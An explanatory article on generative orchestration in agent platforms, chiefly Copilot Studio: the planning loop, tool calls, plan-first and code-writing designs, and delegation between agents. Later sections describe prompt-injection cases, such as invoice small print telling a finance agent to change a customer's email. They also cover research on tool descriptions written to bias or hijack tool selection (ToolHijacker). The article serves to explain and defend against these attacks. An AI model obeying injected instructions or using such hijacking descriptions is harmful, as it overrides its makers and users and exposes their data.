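# Generative orchestration in agent platforms: planning, tool selection and execution without step-by-step approval

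## What is generative orchestration, and how does it differ from a scripted assistant?

Generative orchestration is a way of running a software agent in which a language model works out the steps of a task as the task proceeds. The model reads a request, splits it into parts and picks a function for each part, and ordinary software then runs those functions. Older assistants followed a script that a person had written beforehand. The name comes from Microsoft's Copilot Studio, a product for building business agents with little or no programming.

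In its architecture guidance, Microsoft defines generative orchestration as a planning layer, driven by a language model, that interprets what the user wants, breaks down complex requests, selects tools and knowledge, and executes multi-step plans "with guardrails for safety and compliance". In a shorter definition elsewhere, Microsoft specifies that the agent selects these "at runtime", which is most of what is new. The maker, the person who builds and configures the agent, decides what the model may choose from, but what the agent uses, and in which order, depends on the request and the model.

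An agent in a company's finance department might read a mailbox that receives invoices, search a finance policy file, update customer records and send email. Its orchestrator is the language model and the surrounding software, which together turn an incoming message into a plan, an ordered list of steps for the agent to run. Its tools are the functions the orchestrator can call, such as one that looks up a customer record or one that sends an email. Each tool has a name, a description, and defined inputs and outputs. The policy file is a knowledge source, which the agent can search but not change. Topics are short dialogues that the maker has written out, such as the fixed questions for a customer who disputes a charge.

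The agent may also hand part of a job to a connected agent, perhaps one that the tax team maintains. If both are Copilot Studio agents, they must be in the same environment, and the tax team must have published its agent and opened it to connections, according to Microsoft's *Connect to an existing Copilot Studio agent*. An event trigger, here the arrival of an email, starts the agent without a message from a user. The last component is the runtime, the conventional software that carries out each call and returns the result.

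Most of these parts, such as databases, document search and scheduled jobs, existed long before language models. Microsoft advises makers to test that a tool behaves the same way every time it gets the same inputs, because the orchestrator treats tools as reliable functions. The unpredictable part is which tool the orchestrator calls and with what inputs.

### One request under two designs

Microsoft calls the older method classic orchestration. The maker writes dialogues, called topics, and gives each one trigger phrases, which are sample wordings such as "opening hours" or "when are you open". The agent compares each incoming message with these phrases and runs the topic that matches most closely. The following comparison draws on an archived Microsoft release plan and on Microsoft's *Orchestrate agent behavior with generative AI (preview)*.

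| Behaviour | Classic orchestration | Generative orchestration |
|---|---|---|
| Starting a topic | The message matches the topic's trigger phrases | The request fits the description of the topic's purpose |
| Calling a tool | Happens only inside a topic, where the maker put the call | The agent can call a tool on the basis of its name and description |
| Searching knowledge | A fallback when no topic matches, or an explicit step in a topic | The agent can search at its own initiative |
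| Combining parts | The agent tries to find one topic for the message | The agent can combine topics, tools and knowledge |
| Missing details | The maker writes the question to the user | The agent can write the question |
| Reply | The maker writes it | The agent composes it from the results |

In Microsoft's standard example, a customer writes, "I need to get store hours and find my nearest store." The agent has one topic for hours and another for locating a store, but under classic orchestration it looks for a single topic. If it selects the hours topic, it asks which store the customer means, using the question the maker typed, and then gives the hours. The customer still doesn't know which store is nearest and has to ask again. A maker could prevent this by writing a third topic for the combined request, but would then need to write one for every other likely pair of requests.

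Under generative orchestration, the agent selects both the store locator and hours topics and chains them. If the hours topic needs a store name as input, the agent should run the locator first and pass the name along, without anyone having to script that branch. If the customer then asks "what's the weather like there?", the agent can fill in the town from earlier in the conversation and call a weather tool.

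Generative orchestration also changes how an agent handles ambiguous requests. When a message closely fits several topics, a classic agent normally asks the user to pick one. In its preview documentation, Microsoft listed as a known limitation that generative agents did not call the system topic that asks this question, and in later architecture guidance it explained that the planner handles ambiguity differently. The choice now rests largely with the model. This spares the user a question if the model interprets the request correctly, but otherwise the user may discover the mistake only from the result.

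One agent can combine both designs. An authored topic keeps its fixed steps even when the orchestrator selects it, so the model controls whether a payment dialogue starts but not how it runs. Microsoft recommends fixed steps for payments, deletions and anything else that must happen exactly as specified.

### Planning, choosing and acting without approval

The term "autonomous agent" tends to combine three separable properties: the system plans several steps, chooses its own tools, and acts without a person's approval.

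A clerk who asks a chat model how to close the month's invoices may get back eight steps in a workable order. The model only plans, because it has no tools and the clerk does the work. Another assistant might have forty functions, pick one for each message, fill in the inputs and wait for the clerk to press a button. It chooses tools, but it doesn't plan beyond the next step or act without the clerk's approval.

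Software can act without approval even if it doesn't use a language model. Microsoft's *What's new in Copilot Studio* (2025) introduced agent flows, which follow a predefined sequence of actions and can repeat it hundreds or thousands of times a day. Such a flow could email every customer with an overdue invoice at six each morning, but a person would have planned the sequence and chosen the email function in advance.

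Generative orchestration, in Microsoft's sense, combines planning with tool selection. The people who build an agent, whom Microsoft calls makers, configure when it needs approval. Microsoft asks them to sort the agent's actions into those it can run without confirmation, those the user must confirm in the conversation, and those that someone outside the conversation must approve. Makers are also responsible for enforcing these boundaries. The same orchestrator with the same tools may therefore stop before every change to a record in one company and before none in another. A failure in the second company could come from a bad plan, the wrong tool or a missing check, and each needs a different fix.

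Event triggers are a separate matter because they concern how a task starts. An agent that starts when an email arrives can still hold its reply until a manager approves it, and an agent that a user starts in a chat can run ten steps without asking for approval. In practice, though, triggers make approval harder to arrange because nobody is in the conversation to confirm an action. The maker has to send the request to someone elsewhere or let the agent act without approval.

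### From generative actions to persistent agents

Microsoft presented the idea at its Build conference in 2023 as "generative actions", a feature then in limited preview in Power Virtual Agents, which later became Copilot Studio. Microsoft's *Reinvent your AI assistants with generative answers, actions, and more* (2023) describes how a maker pointed the bot at a collection of the company's APIs, the interfaces through which programs call one another. The bot picked the APIs that could fulfil a request, chained them and generated questions for any missing details. In early preview documentation for Copilot Studio, the model drew up a plan and reassessed it after each new message from the user.

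Microsoft's release plan, *Use generative actions*, gave June 2024 as the date for general availability, when Microsoft supports a feature for production use. The feature became generally available in March 2025, under the name generative orchestration and for agents in US English.

Microsoft (2024) separately announced event triggers, which would let agents react to events or run on a schedule without human input. The triggers entered public preview at Microsoft's Ignite conference that November. In one example from that month's *What’s new in Copilot Studio*, an agent runs whenever someone adds a row to a table in SAP, a widely used business database system. The agent summarises the case, looks up the worker responsible and emails that person the relevant documents. These triggers, too, became generally available in March 2025.

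Microsoft later announced orchestration across several agents at Build in May 2025, in *Multi-agent orchestration, maker controls, and more* (2025). According to Microsoft's *New and improved* (2026), eligible customers would be able to connect to three more kinds of agent by April 2026: those in Fabric, Microsoft's data platform; those that developers build with its Microsoft 365 toolkit; and those from any supplier that supports an open protocol called Agent-to-Agent. In Microsoft's example, a bank customer asks about a mortgage payment and an account balance in one message and gets a single answer that draws on the loan department's agent and the banking department's agent.

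The latest step came on 15 October 2026, when *Delegate shared business processes to agents that are more persistent and proactive* (Moore, 2026) announced agents with their own accounts, memory and triggers for recurring business processes. Having its own account changes whose authority an agent uses. Microsoft's FAQ on generative orchestration describes a different arrangement, in which an agent with an event trigger and the tools it calls work only with the credentials of the agent's maker.

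Over these three years, successive Microsoft releases let software, rather than people, decide which function to call, when to begin, and which agent should do the work. None of these releases required makers to give up approval. The March 2025 announcement still described agents asking for confirmation "when needed" before an action.

Other companies built the same arrangement under other names. In 2023, Amazon introduced agents for Bedrock, its service for running language models. Developers described a set of APIs, and the model broke a request into steps and chose which API to call for each. Salesforce launched Agentforce in 2024 with what it called a reasoning engine, which matched a customer's request to a topic and then chose from the actions available for that topic. Coding agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code work the same way. Their tools read files, edit them and run commands,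 and a programmer can have the agent ask before it acts or let it proceed without asking. The defaults for approval differ among these products, but in each case a model chooses functions from a list and other software runs them.

### What the model reads and writes

A language model keeps no record of a task between calls. Each time the software calls it, the model receives text, called its context, and produces a continuation using only that text and what it learned in training. For the finance agent, the context would contain the maker's instructions, the tool metadata (the names, descriptions and input definitions of the tools), the email that started the run, any passages from the policy file and the results of earlier calls. In a chat, Copilot Studio also uses the last ten turns of the conversation.

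The model cannot change a customer record. It can only write text asking for the change, and this text is a tool call. Formats vary between suppliers, but a call from the finance agent might look like this:

```
{
  "tool": "update_customer_record",
  "inputs": {
    "customer_id": "C-1042",
    "billing_email": "accounts@example.com"
  }
}
```

The runtime reads these lines, runs the named tool with those inputs and adds the result to the context. The orchestrator can then propose another call or write a reply. A person or a program could still refuse a call before the runtime executes it, but they often have only a fraction of a second to do so. The model cannot unsend an email after the runtime has sent it.

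Makers can connect each tool by hand or use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic published in 2024. Under MCP, a tool's operator puts it behind a server, which gives agents a list of its tools and their metadata. Copilot Studio added MCP support in public preview in March 2025. Its connectors import each tool's name, description, inputs and outputs from the server and update them when the server's operator changes them. This saves makers a good deal of maintenance, but it also means that someone outside the company may write, and later change, some of the text the orchestrator uses to choose tools.

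All this text reaches the model through the same channel. Software can label one passage as the maker's instructions and another as an email from a stranger, and developers train models to respect such labels, but the model still has to interpret both as language. In prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by supplying text that the model follows as an instruction, against the wishes of the maker or the user. In direct prompt injection, the attacker types the text into the conversation, for instance telling a customer service agent to disregard its rules and reveal another customer's address.

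In indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants instructions in untrusted content, which is text the agent reads that someone other than its user or maker could have written. The finance agent's mailbox is full of such text. A supplier's invoice might include small print telling any system that processes it to replace the email address on a customer's record and send a confirmation. The attacker needs no account at the company and no direct contact with the agent, which only has to open the invoice during its ordinary work. Microsoft lists four places where Copilot Studio looks for malicious instructions: user input, trigger data, tool outputs and knowledge content. Direct injection comes through user input, while a stranger's text can enter through any of the other three. With an event trigger, that text can reach the agent before anyone at the company has read it.

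## How does the orchestrator turn a request into a series of tool calls?

The orchestrator runs a loop. It gathers the text the model needs, gets a proposed step from the model, has the runtime carry out that step, adds the result to the text and goes round again. Dehghantanha (2026), in *SoK*, a survey of the security of such agents, reduces the cycle to four operations: plan, select a tool, execute, update state. They repeat until the agent meets its goal, exhausts its budget or refuses to go on. With the checks that a business platform adds, the loop looks roughly like this:

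```
history = recent turns, if any
while budget remains:
    context = instructions + goal + tool_metadata + history
    action  = model(context)
    if action is a final reply:
        return action
    if action lacks a required input:
        history += ask_user(missing_input)
        continue
    if not valid(action) or not allowed(action):
        history += error          # some platforms end the run here
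        continue
    result   = runtime.execute(action)
    history += (action, result)
```

Control theorists call a rule of this kind a policy, meaning a function from the current situation to the next action:

next action = f(instructions, goal, history of calls and results, available tools)

The maker writes the instructions and picks the tools, and the user or an event trigger supplies the goal. The tools' results are added to the history during the run, so nobody can review it in advance. Two runs that begin identically can diverge as soon as one search returns a different passage. Suppliers also usually have the model choose its words partly at random, so f can give different outputs for the same inputs.

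### One pass through the loop

Microsoft's *Orchestration with Copilot Studio*, a training lab for makers, explains that each pass starts with the context, which includes the agent's general instructions on every turn. The instructions of a child agent, a smaller agent inside the main one, are added only when the orchestrator has selected that child. General instructions take up space every time, and Microsoft advises makers to reserve them for rules that always apply, such as "Never offer to export or create a file."

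In a chat, the orchestrator also uses the last ten turns. According to Microsoft, a run that starts from an event has no turns, so the orchestrator uses the event's data, the trigger's instructions and the agent's own instructions. Microsoft was already giving the ten-turn figure in June 2025 and had not changed it by May 2026. The figure predates the second orchestration engine, which Microsoft released that August, so it may not apply to that engine.

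The model then proposes a step by choosing a tool and filling in its inputs. It bases the choice largely on the tools' names and descriptions. The maker can set an input's value in advance, as in Microsoft's lab, where the weather tool always reports in metric units. Otherwise the model takes the value from the conversation or from the output of an earlier call. When a user in the lab asks for the accounts in Texas, the model passes "TX" to the search tool because the input's description specifies a two-letter state code in capitals. A search for "Texas" would have returned nothing. A clear description makes the right format more likely but doesn't guarantee it, because a language model does the converting. Microsoft therefore overstates the case when it calls such conversions between steps deterministic if makers describe the inputs well.

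If a required input is missing, the agent writes a question based on the input's name and description, so Microsoft tells makers to choose names a person would understand, such as "start date". When an incoming email starts the agent, there is nobody in the conversation to ask. The maker has to plan for missing inputs, perhaps with a default value or an instruction to write back to the sender.

Validation comes next. Dehghantanha treats the model as an "untrusted code generator", whose output other software must validate before anything runs. Part of this is routine checking of input values. In Copilot Studio, a maker can write a formula that holds a country code to two letters or limits an email's recipients to one domain. Such a formula can miss a wrong value that is correctly formatted. If the customer is C-1042, a rule about the format of customer numbers will also accept C-1024. The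 platform can also submit each proposed call to a separate security service for a runtime check, an automated decision to allow or block the call.

The runtime then executes the call. Microsoft says that in the Copilot assistant, a component separate from the orchestrator sends the request and returns the result. Some tools use language models themselves, so they may not behave as consistently as Microsoft asks. *Inside Copilot Studio*, the security firm Pluto Security's account of its own tests, found that a single turn could involve three language models. By default, Claude Sonnet 4.6 ran the orchestrator, GPT-4.1 mini answered prompts inside one tool, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 operated a web browser inside another.

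Finally, the orchestrator either continues or stops. Earlier Microsoft documentation, quoted in SharePoint Europe's *Microsoft Copilot Studio*, describes a check before each reply. If the system has not found an answer to the user's question, it repeats the process. Copilot's loop runs until the model determines that it should write a final response. The model's output therefore controls when the loop stops, and only a cap on steps or spending applies regardless of that output.

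Makers can review this process afterwards. Pluto Security found that Copilot Studio logs an event for each step of a plan, along with the model's stated reason for taking it. Microsoft's lab also recommends using the "Get rationale" button, which produces a plain-language account of the plan, to find badly worded descriptions. It may well help with that, but the account is also generated by a language model, and a plausible reason doesn't establish what actually produced the choice.

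### An ordinary invoice, call by call

The finance agent with the invoice mailbox comes from a Microsoft security article, which traces what happens when the agent receives a hostile email. Its instructions limit it to invoice data and basic finance questions. The run below uses the same set-up but is harmless, and its tool names and values are made up.

A company writes from accounts@example.com about its account, C-1042. It has sent invoice 7781 for £1,840, dated 2 March 2026, and asks the finance department to record it and say when payment will come. The context now holds the agent's instructions, the metadata of its tools and the email, with no history yet. The email contains everything needed for the record except a payment date. The policy search is the only tool whose description mentions payment terms, so the model proposes that first:

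```
search_policy(query = "payment terms for invoices")
result: "Invoices under £5,000 are payable 30 days after the invoice date."
```

The policy file is a knowledge source, but the search goes through the same loop as a tool call. It returns a rule, which the model applies to the amount and date in the email. Without using a tool, the model works out that the invoice is under £5,000 and that 30 days after 2 March is 1 April. Similarly, an agent in Microsoft's lab that needs a contact's age retrieves her date of birth and calculates the age itself. The lab recommends using a tool when a calculation depends on exact business rules, and a cautious maker might do so for payment dates.

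The model can now fill every input of the record update:

```
update_customer_record(
    customer_id = "C-1042",
    invoice_no  = "7781",
    amount_gbp  = 1840,
    due_date    = "2026-04-01")
result: status = "updated"
```

The update comes before the email because the email will state that the company has recorded the invoice. If the database had returned an error, that statement would have been false, and the agent could not have recalled the message. With "updated" in the context, the model proposes the last call:

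```
send_email(
    to      = "accounts@example.com",
    subject = "Invoice 7781 received",
    body    = "We have recorded invoice 7781 for £1,840.
               Payment is due on 1 April 2026.")
result: status = "sent"
```

On its fourth pass the model has nothing left to do, so it ends the run with a short note for the log. The run took three tool calls and four model calls. If the company has connected Microsoft's Defender service, Copilot Studio also sends Defender the details of each proposed tool call, including the inputs and the results so far, and waits for permission. Every value in the updated record except the due date came from the email, so even in this innocent case an outsider wrote most of what the agent put into the database.

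### Deciding step by step, planning ahead or writing a program

In the invoice run, the model chose each step after reading the previous result. If the policy file had required staff to return any invoice without a purchase order number, the model would have read this before touching the record and could have gone straight to an email asking for the number.

*ReAct* (Yao, Zhao, Yu and colleagues, 2022) gave this method its usual name. The model alternated between writing a line of reasoning and taking an action, and read the outcome before continuing. With only one or two worked examples in the prompt, its success rate was 34 percentage points higher in a simulated household, and 10 points higher in a simulated web shop, than those of systems trained by imitation or reinforcement learning.

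The drawback is that the model rereads everything at every step, and suppliers charge by the token, which is a word or part of a word. If the opening context has B tokens and each tool call with its result adds d more, a run of n tool calls takes n + 1 model calls, which together read (n + 1)B + dn(n + 1)/2 tokens. The second term grows with the square of the number of steps. Suppliers often discount text they have recently processed, which lowers the bill, but the model calls must still run one after another.

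Xu, Peng, Lei and colleagues (2023) removed most of the rereading in *ReWOO*. Their model writes the entire plan before any tool runs and uses placeholders for results that don't exist yet. For the invoice, the plan might be:

```
E1 = search_policy("payment terms for invoices")
E2 = work_out_due_date("2026-03-02", E1)
E3 = update_customer_record("C-1042", "7781", 1840, E2)
E4 = send_email("accounts@example.com", confirmation with E2)
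```

The runtime carries out the steps in order, then makes one more model call to write the answer from the collected results. The second line is necessary because the search returns a sentence and the database requires a date. ReWOO lets a plan include a small model call to extract it. On HotpotQA, a set of questions that need facts from more than one Wikipedia article, Xu and colleagues reported a fivefold gain in token efficiency and a 4 per cent improvement in accuracy.

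*An LLM Compiler for Parallel Function Calling* (Kim, Moon, Tabrizi and colleagues, 2023) describes a planner that also records which steps depend on which, so that the runtime can run independent steps at the same time. In the paper's tests, this approach was up to 3.7 times as fast as ReAct, cut costs by a factor of up to 6.7 and improved accuracy by up to about 9 per cent. Parallel calls would help a good deal when an agent has to fetch the details of four separate accounts, but they would help the invoice agent little because each of its steps needs the one before.

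These results seem to favour planning first on every measure, but Xu, Kim and their colleagues used 2023 models and mostly set tasks whose steps a planner could foresee. The steps in web navigation are harder to foresee because each page determines what the agent can do next. Erdogan, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) tested this in *Plan-and-Act*, using WebArena-Lite, a set of tasks on simulated websites. Letting the planner revise its plan after each step raised the success rate by about ten percentage points, to roughly 54 per cent, but it also brought back the repeated model calls that planning ahead had avoided.

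A model can also write a program that calls the tools. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen, Yuan and colleagues, 2024) tested 17 models and found success rates up to 20 per cent higher when they acted by writing Python than when they wrote calls in text or JSON, a common data format. Because programs can contain conditions and loops, one model call could produce a program that handles invoices with or without a purchase order number, or makes the same change to 200 customer records.

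Intermediate results stay in the program's variables, and only what the program prints goes back to the model. Anthropic (2025) tested this on its own product and reported in *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* that it cut average token use on complex research tasks by 37 per cent, from 43,588 to 27,297. Accuracy on an internal retrieval test rose slightly, from 25.6 to 28.5 per cent. Anthropic also noted that a program with 20 tool calls reduces delay by avoiding at least 19 passes through the model.

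Programs have a disadvantage when the tools they call make changes. If a program that updates customer records crashes at the 120th customer, it has already changed 119 records, and the model receives the error only afterwards.

The table shows how many tokens the model reads if the context starts at 3,000 tokens and each step adds 500. The program and its printed output are also assumed to total 500 tokens. The figures are illustrative, not measured.

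| Method | Model calls | Tokens read, 3 tool calls | Tokens read, 20 tool calls | After an unexpected result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Decide after each result | One per tool call, plus one | 15,000 | 168,000 | The next step can change |
| Write the plan first | 2 | 7,500 | 16,000 | The plan continues, unless the design allows revision |
| Write a program | 2 | 6,500 | 6,500 | The program can take only the branches it contains |

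Copilot Studio began with a design close to plan-first. In Microsoft's *Orchestrate copilot topics and actions with generative AI (preview)*, the agent selects its topics and actions, then generates a plan that sets their order. Microsoft's *Order Management with Enhanced Task Completion*, a sample for developers, calls this model "plan-then-execute". The training lab simplifies it to "single-pass", although the lab's own agent makes four calls in response to one message. In November 2026, Microsoft described the standard engine as making several isolated model calls per turn and returning control to the user once a step needs input.

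With Enhanced Task Completion, which Microsoft introduced as an experimental setting, the agent decides what to do next after each result. In the lab, a user asks for a gift idea for the main contact at a company called Litware, and the gift has to fit company policy and the local weather. The agent finds the contact and her city, searches the gift policy, checks the city's weather and then suggests gifts, all in one turn. According to the lab, each tool call would typically end the turn under the standard engine. Microsoft's guide *Enhanced Task Completion* adds that the agent runs independent calls in parallel and, if a call fails, retries with corrected inputs or looks for another way.

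In August 2026, Microsoft made a new engine for such work generally available alongside the standard one. It first called the engine the GitHub Copilot harness and later the Microsoft Copilot harness. In *Copilot Studio's New Harness*, powerplatstack explains that a harness is the layer of software around the model that runs the loop. Microsoft recommends the new harness for jobs that combine reasoning with several actions, and gives the example of an accounts payable agent that matches invoices to purchase orders and sends exceptions to someone for approval.

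Under the adaptive setting, the agent also writes programs when it has no suitable tool. Later in the lab, the user asks for a table as an Excel file, and the agent writes and runs a short script because the maker has connected no tool that can produce one. Microsoft's FAQ on generative orchestration lists as a safeguard that agents use only the tools, topics, knowledge and agents that the maker has configured. That holds for the standard engine in the lab, but makers can't rely on it under the adaptive setting. Microsoft does warn makers to watch for code execution and decide whether it suits the job.

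Makers gave up some features for this flexibility. When the lab was published, Enhanced Task Completion did not support topics, child agents, evaluation runs or the usual activity history, although makers could still open individual steps in the test window. *Copilot Studio Harnesses* (Pentyala, 2026) notes that even building and testing an agent on the new harness consumes paid credits. Microsoft's lab and sample describe how the two approaches differ but give no figures for accuracy, tokens or delay, so a company choosing between them would have to test both on its own invoices.

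### Handing part of the task to another agent

The orchestrator passes structured inputs, such as a customer number, to a tool, but it gives another agent its task as a sentence. In Microsoft's lab, a user who has been looking through a list of accounts asks, "What is the job title of the primary contact of the 2nd one?" The orchestrator uses earlier results to identify the company and person, then sends its contacts agent the task of getting the job title of Nancy Anderson, the primary contact for Adventure Works. The contacts agent runs its own loop, with its own instructions and tools, and returns a summary that names the tool it called and gives the answer, "Purchasing Assistant". The orchestrator writes its reply from that summary.

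Delegation can happen in the middle of a longer chain. In Microsoft's order management sample, a customer asks when his unshipped games console will arrive and what he can do if it is out of stock. The orders agent has tools for finding his order, but a warehouse agent with four tools of its own handles stock levels and restocking dates. The orders agent passes that part of the question to the warehouse agent and doesn't need to track which of those tools it uses.

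The receiving agent may not get the user's original message. Copilot Studio passes it what Microsoft calls relevant context, and when the agent is external, the maker can choose whether to include the full conversation. Including it lets the receiving agent check the task against the user's own words, but uses more tokens and discloses more to whoever operates that agent. An agent that receives only the task will repeat any mistake the orchestrator made in interpreting the request. If the orchestrator had picked the wrong account from the list, the contacts agent would have reported the wrong person's job, even though its own lookup was correct.

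Developers train models to distinguish a few sources of text, chiefly the developer's instructions, the user and the results of tools. When one agent sends a task to another, agent software commonly puts the task where the user's message would go, so the receiving agent treats it as the user's request. In the policy above, the first agent's output becomes the second agent's goal.

In the Agent-to-Agent protocol, which Microsoft has made generally available in Copilot Studio, every message has one of two roles, "user" or "agent", and the agent that requests the work sends its messages as "user". Anthropic takes the same approach in the constitution it published for its Claude models in 2026. Under it, a Claude model that directs other agents acts as their operator or user, and should treat what they send back as information, not instructions.

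This makes agents easy to combine, since one that can serve a person can serve another agent without changes. It also gives the orchestrator's sentence the authority of a user's request, although the label "user" doesn't show where the sentence came from. For example, the finance agent might ask the tax team's agent to mark invoice 7781 as exempt from VAT. The tax agent would receive the same sentence whether the exemption claim came from a manager, the policy file or a line in the supplier's email.

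## How does it choose among connected tools, and who can sway the choice?

The orchestrator's model chooses a tool by reading its metadata and does not see the code behind it. Faghih, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Gaming Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs*, note that this is true of OpenAI's function calling, the common developer libraries and MCP. Whoever writes the metadata therefore influences which tools the model chooses.

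### Names, descriptions and a wrong call

Microsoft has changed its guidance on which text matters most when the agent chooses a tool. Its preview documentation for Copilot Studio called the description "the most important factor", ahead of the name and the inputs, but its 2026 guidance says "Names carry more weight than descriptions." The training lab also puts names first, with the description as a tiebreaker between similar names. Microsoft gives no measurements for either claim. It may have changed the engine in between or learned more about how it behaves, but in either case makers have to get both the name and the description right.

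Suppose the finance agent has two tools that involve addresses. One is `update_customer_record`, with the description "Updates customer details, such as address and billing email." The other sends a single payment notice to a different address, but its maker left it with the name "Flow1" and the description "Runs the update." A customer writes, "Please send the payment notice for invoice 7781 to our Leeds office." Only the first tool's description mentions addresses, so the model chooses it and overwrites the customer's permanent record. The call is valid because the customer exists and the address is real, so the database returns "updated" and every later notice goes to Leeds.

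A name such as "Redirect One Payment Notice" would probably prevent this, especially with a description saying that the tool doesn't change the customer record. Microsoft's preview documentation also recommends saying what a tool can't do, in its example of two weather tools, one for current conditions and one for tomorrow's forecast. Such descriptions are still easy to get wrong. Microsoft's sample description for the current-weather tool begins by saying that it provides a "weather forecast".

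According to Anthropic, the most common failures are choosing the wrong tool and giving it the wrong inputs, especially when tools have similar names, such as `notification-send-user` and `notification-send-channel`. In the company's internal tests, adding sample calls to the tool definitions raised accuracy on complex inputs from 72 to 90 per cent.

When an agent keeps picking the wrong tool, Microsoft's lab tells makers to fix the tool's name first, then add words users are likely to say to its description, and then write an instruction that points to the tool. Makers can also restrict a tool to one child agent, so the model has fewer tools to compare. Microsoft's guidance adds that overlapping descriptions can make an agent try several tools at once. This wastes a little time if the tools only search, but if they change records, someone has to correct the unwanted changes.

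### When the catalogue outgrows the context

The finance agent's few tools fit easily into the context, but larger sets don't. Anthropic found that the definitions of 58 tools across five common services, including GitHub and Slack, took up about 55,000 tokens before the user made a request. It had also seen set-ups in which definitions took up 134,000 tokens.

The usual remedy is to filter the tools first and let the model choose from what remains. Shi, Yuan and colleagues (2025), in *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents*, set out the method formally. For a request q and a library D of n tool documents, it has two stages:

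```
1. Retrieve:  D_k = the k documents d in D with the highest Sim(f(q), g(d))
2. Choose:    d*  = model(q, D_k)
```

Here f and g turn the request and each tool document into vectors, which are lists of numbers. Texts with similar meanings have vectors that are close together, and sim measures that closeness, for instance by the angle between the vectors. The model receives only the k documents from the first stage, so if the right tool isn't among them, the model can't choose it.

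Production systems generally combine such a filter with the model's own choice, according to *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026). In Anthropic's version, the model starts with a single search tool, uses it to look for the tools it needs and loads the full definitions of the three to five best matches. In the company's tests, this cut token use by 85 per cent. Accuracy rose from 49 to 74 per cent for Claude Opus 4 and from 79.5 to 88.1 per cent for the newer Opus 4.5. The smaller gain suggests that stronger models cope better with a crowded context, but the evidence is weak because it covers only two models, both from Anthropic, and the company doesn't describe the test tasks.

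*Scalable LLM Agent Tool Access in the Cloud* (2026) reports that a model with every tool definition in its context picked the right tool 92.4 per cent of the time from 15 tools, but only 78.2 per cent from 640. On a second set, from Alibaba's cloud business, the definitions no longer fitted in the context at 752 tools. A hybrid search that passed 15 candidates to the model still reached 81.6 per cent with 3,616 tools.

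In the same test, an earlier method called RAG-MCP reached 72.1 per cent. *MCP-Zero* (2025) describes RAG-MCP as matching the request to a whole MCP server and giving the model all of that server's tools. The cloud comparison ran it as a search by meaning alone, so the score may not reflect the original design.

Retrieval studies often report a hit rate instead, the share of requests for which the right tool is among those retrieved. *Semantic Tool Discovery for Large Language Models* (2026) achieved a hit rate of 97.1 per cent when it retrieved three tools out of 121, and used 99.6 per cent fewer tokens. If each request had only one right tool, three tools drawn at random would include it about 2.5 per cent of the time, so the search did far better than chance.

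A high hit rate means much less when the retriever passes many tools to the model. If four of 58 tools suit a task, 20 tools drawn at random will include at least one of them 83 per cent of the time. *The 99% Success Paradox* (2026) makes this argument and reports that models were 10 to 16 percentage points less accurate with 100 candidates than with 10, and used ten times as many tokens.

*Explore Separately, Adopt Selectively* (2026) describes a different failure, in which the search passes on too few tools and can leave out one that the task needs only later. For example, given an email asking the finance agent to record an invoice, a retriever would find the record update tool but might miss the policy search tool, whose description mentions payment terms. In the paper's method, separate branches find tools and try them out before the agent adopts anything, which suits lookups better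 than sending email.

Filtering also doesn't always help current models. *TRACER* (2026) tested a retrieval method on four models and found that three of them chose more accurately from 5 tools than from the full list of 128. GPT-5.4 gained 4.7 percentage points. But on a banking test, GPT-5.4 and Grok-4 did better with the full list than with the best filtered version, by 3.4 and 2.1 points. Anthropic recommends tool search for agents with ten or more tools or more than 10,000 tokens of tool definitions, so by that rule the finance agent doesn't need it. For agents that use search, Anthropic suggests always keeping the three to five most-used tools loaded.

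### How wording alone shifts the choice

Tool suppliers have a reason to write descriptions that persuade models to choose their tools. Faghih and colleagues measured how well this works with test cases from the Berkeley Function-Calling Leaderboard, a standard test of whether models call functions correctly. Each case had one request and one suitable tool. The researchers added a copy of the tool with the same function and inputs, changed only the copy's description, and counted how often the model used each version correctly.

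The researchers ran every comparison in both orders to control for a bias towards whichever tool came first. With two identical descriptions, GPT-4.1 correctly used the first tool in 80.2 per cent of cases and the second in 13.6 per cent. Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, never used the second correctly.

The most effective single edit added a sentence claiming that the function was the best for its purpose and should be used whenever possible. GPT-4.1 then used the edited tool 7.5 times as often as the original, and Qwen2.5-7B 7.8 times as often. Combining several edits raised the ratio above 11 for both models. A claim that the tool was actively maintained led GPT-4.1 to use it 4.3 times as often as the original, but Qwen only 1.8 times as often. Mentioning a well-known company or person increased GPT-4.1's use of the tool by up to 44 per cent and barely affected Qwen's. Across ten models,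 the tool with the assertive sentence was used 81.8 per cent of the time and the original 7.3 per cent.

These tests show how a model chooses between two tools that do the same thing, when picking the advertised one doesn't make the result worse. They don't establish that a promotional claim could get an email tool chosen for a database search. They also can't settle Microsoft's question about names and descriptions, because the tools' names differed only in the final digit. But near-identical tools are common in public catalogues, where several suppliers may offer the same map search or currency conversion. There, one promotional sentence could determine which supplier gets the business and the data.

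Rewriting tool descriptions in neutral language is an easy remedy for this kind of influence. *ToolTweak* (2025) repeated the experiment and found a similar advantage for the edited tool, of up to about 6.5 times. When the researchers had the descriptions rewritten neutrally, the models used the edited tool slightly less often than the original. A maker can also prevent tools from competing by connecting only one for each job.

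The same paper had a language model improve a tool's name and description over several rounds, using the selection results as feedback. In one round, the model copied the name of a more popular rival.

### A hostile tool that wins the search

An attacker can take this much further than a supplier would. Shi and colleagues built an attack called ToolHijacker, in which the attacker publishes one tool in an open catalogue and tries to have agents choose it for a particular task. The attacker can't see the agent's other tools, the retriever, the model or the value of k, and so builds substitutes for all of them. With m sample requests, a substitute library D' and a malicious tool document t, the aim is to find the t that maximises

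```
(1/m) × the number of sample requests q_i for which
        model'(q_i, TopK'(q_i; D' + t)) = t
```

The attack places the attacker's tool document in the library used by the two-stage method described earlier. To pass both stages, the researchers split the tool's description into two parts. The first resembles likely requests so that the retriever ranks the tool highly, and the second is written to make the model select it over the other candidates.

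Shi and colleagues tested the attack on eight models and four retrievers. With Llama-3.3-70B as the substitute model and GPT-4o as the target, the attack succeeded in 96.43 per cent of attempts on MetaTool, a public set of tool-selection tasks. The malicious tool got through the retrieval stage every time.

The researchers then tried existing defences. One, StruQ, trains a model to separate instructions from data, but the attack still succeeded in 99.71 per cent of cases. A detector that looks for passages of improbable text, set to flag under 1 per cent of harmless descriptions, missed 85.71 per cent of the malicious ones written by a language model. Those descriptions are fluent prose, so they contain few improbable passages.

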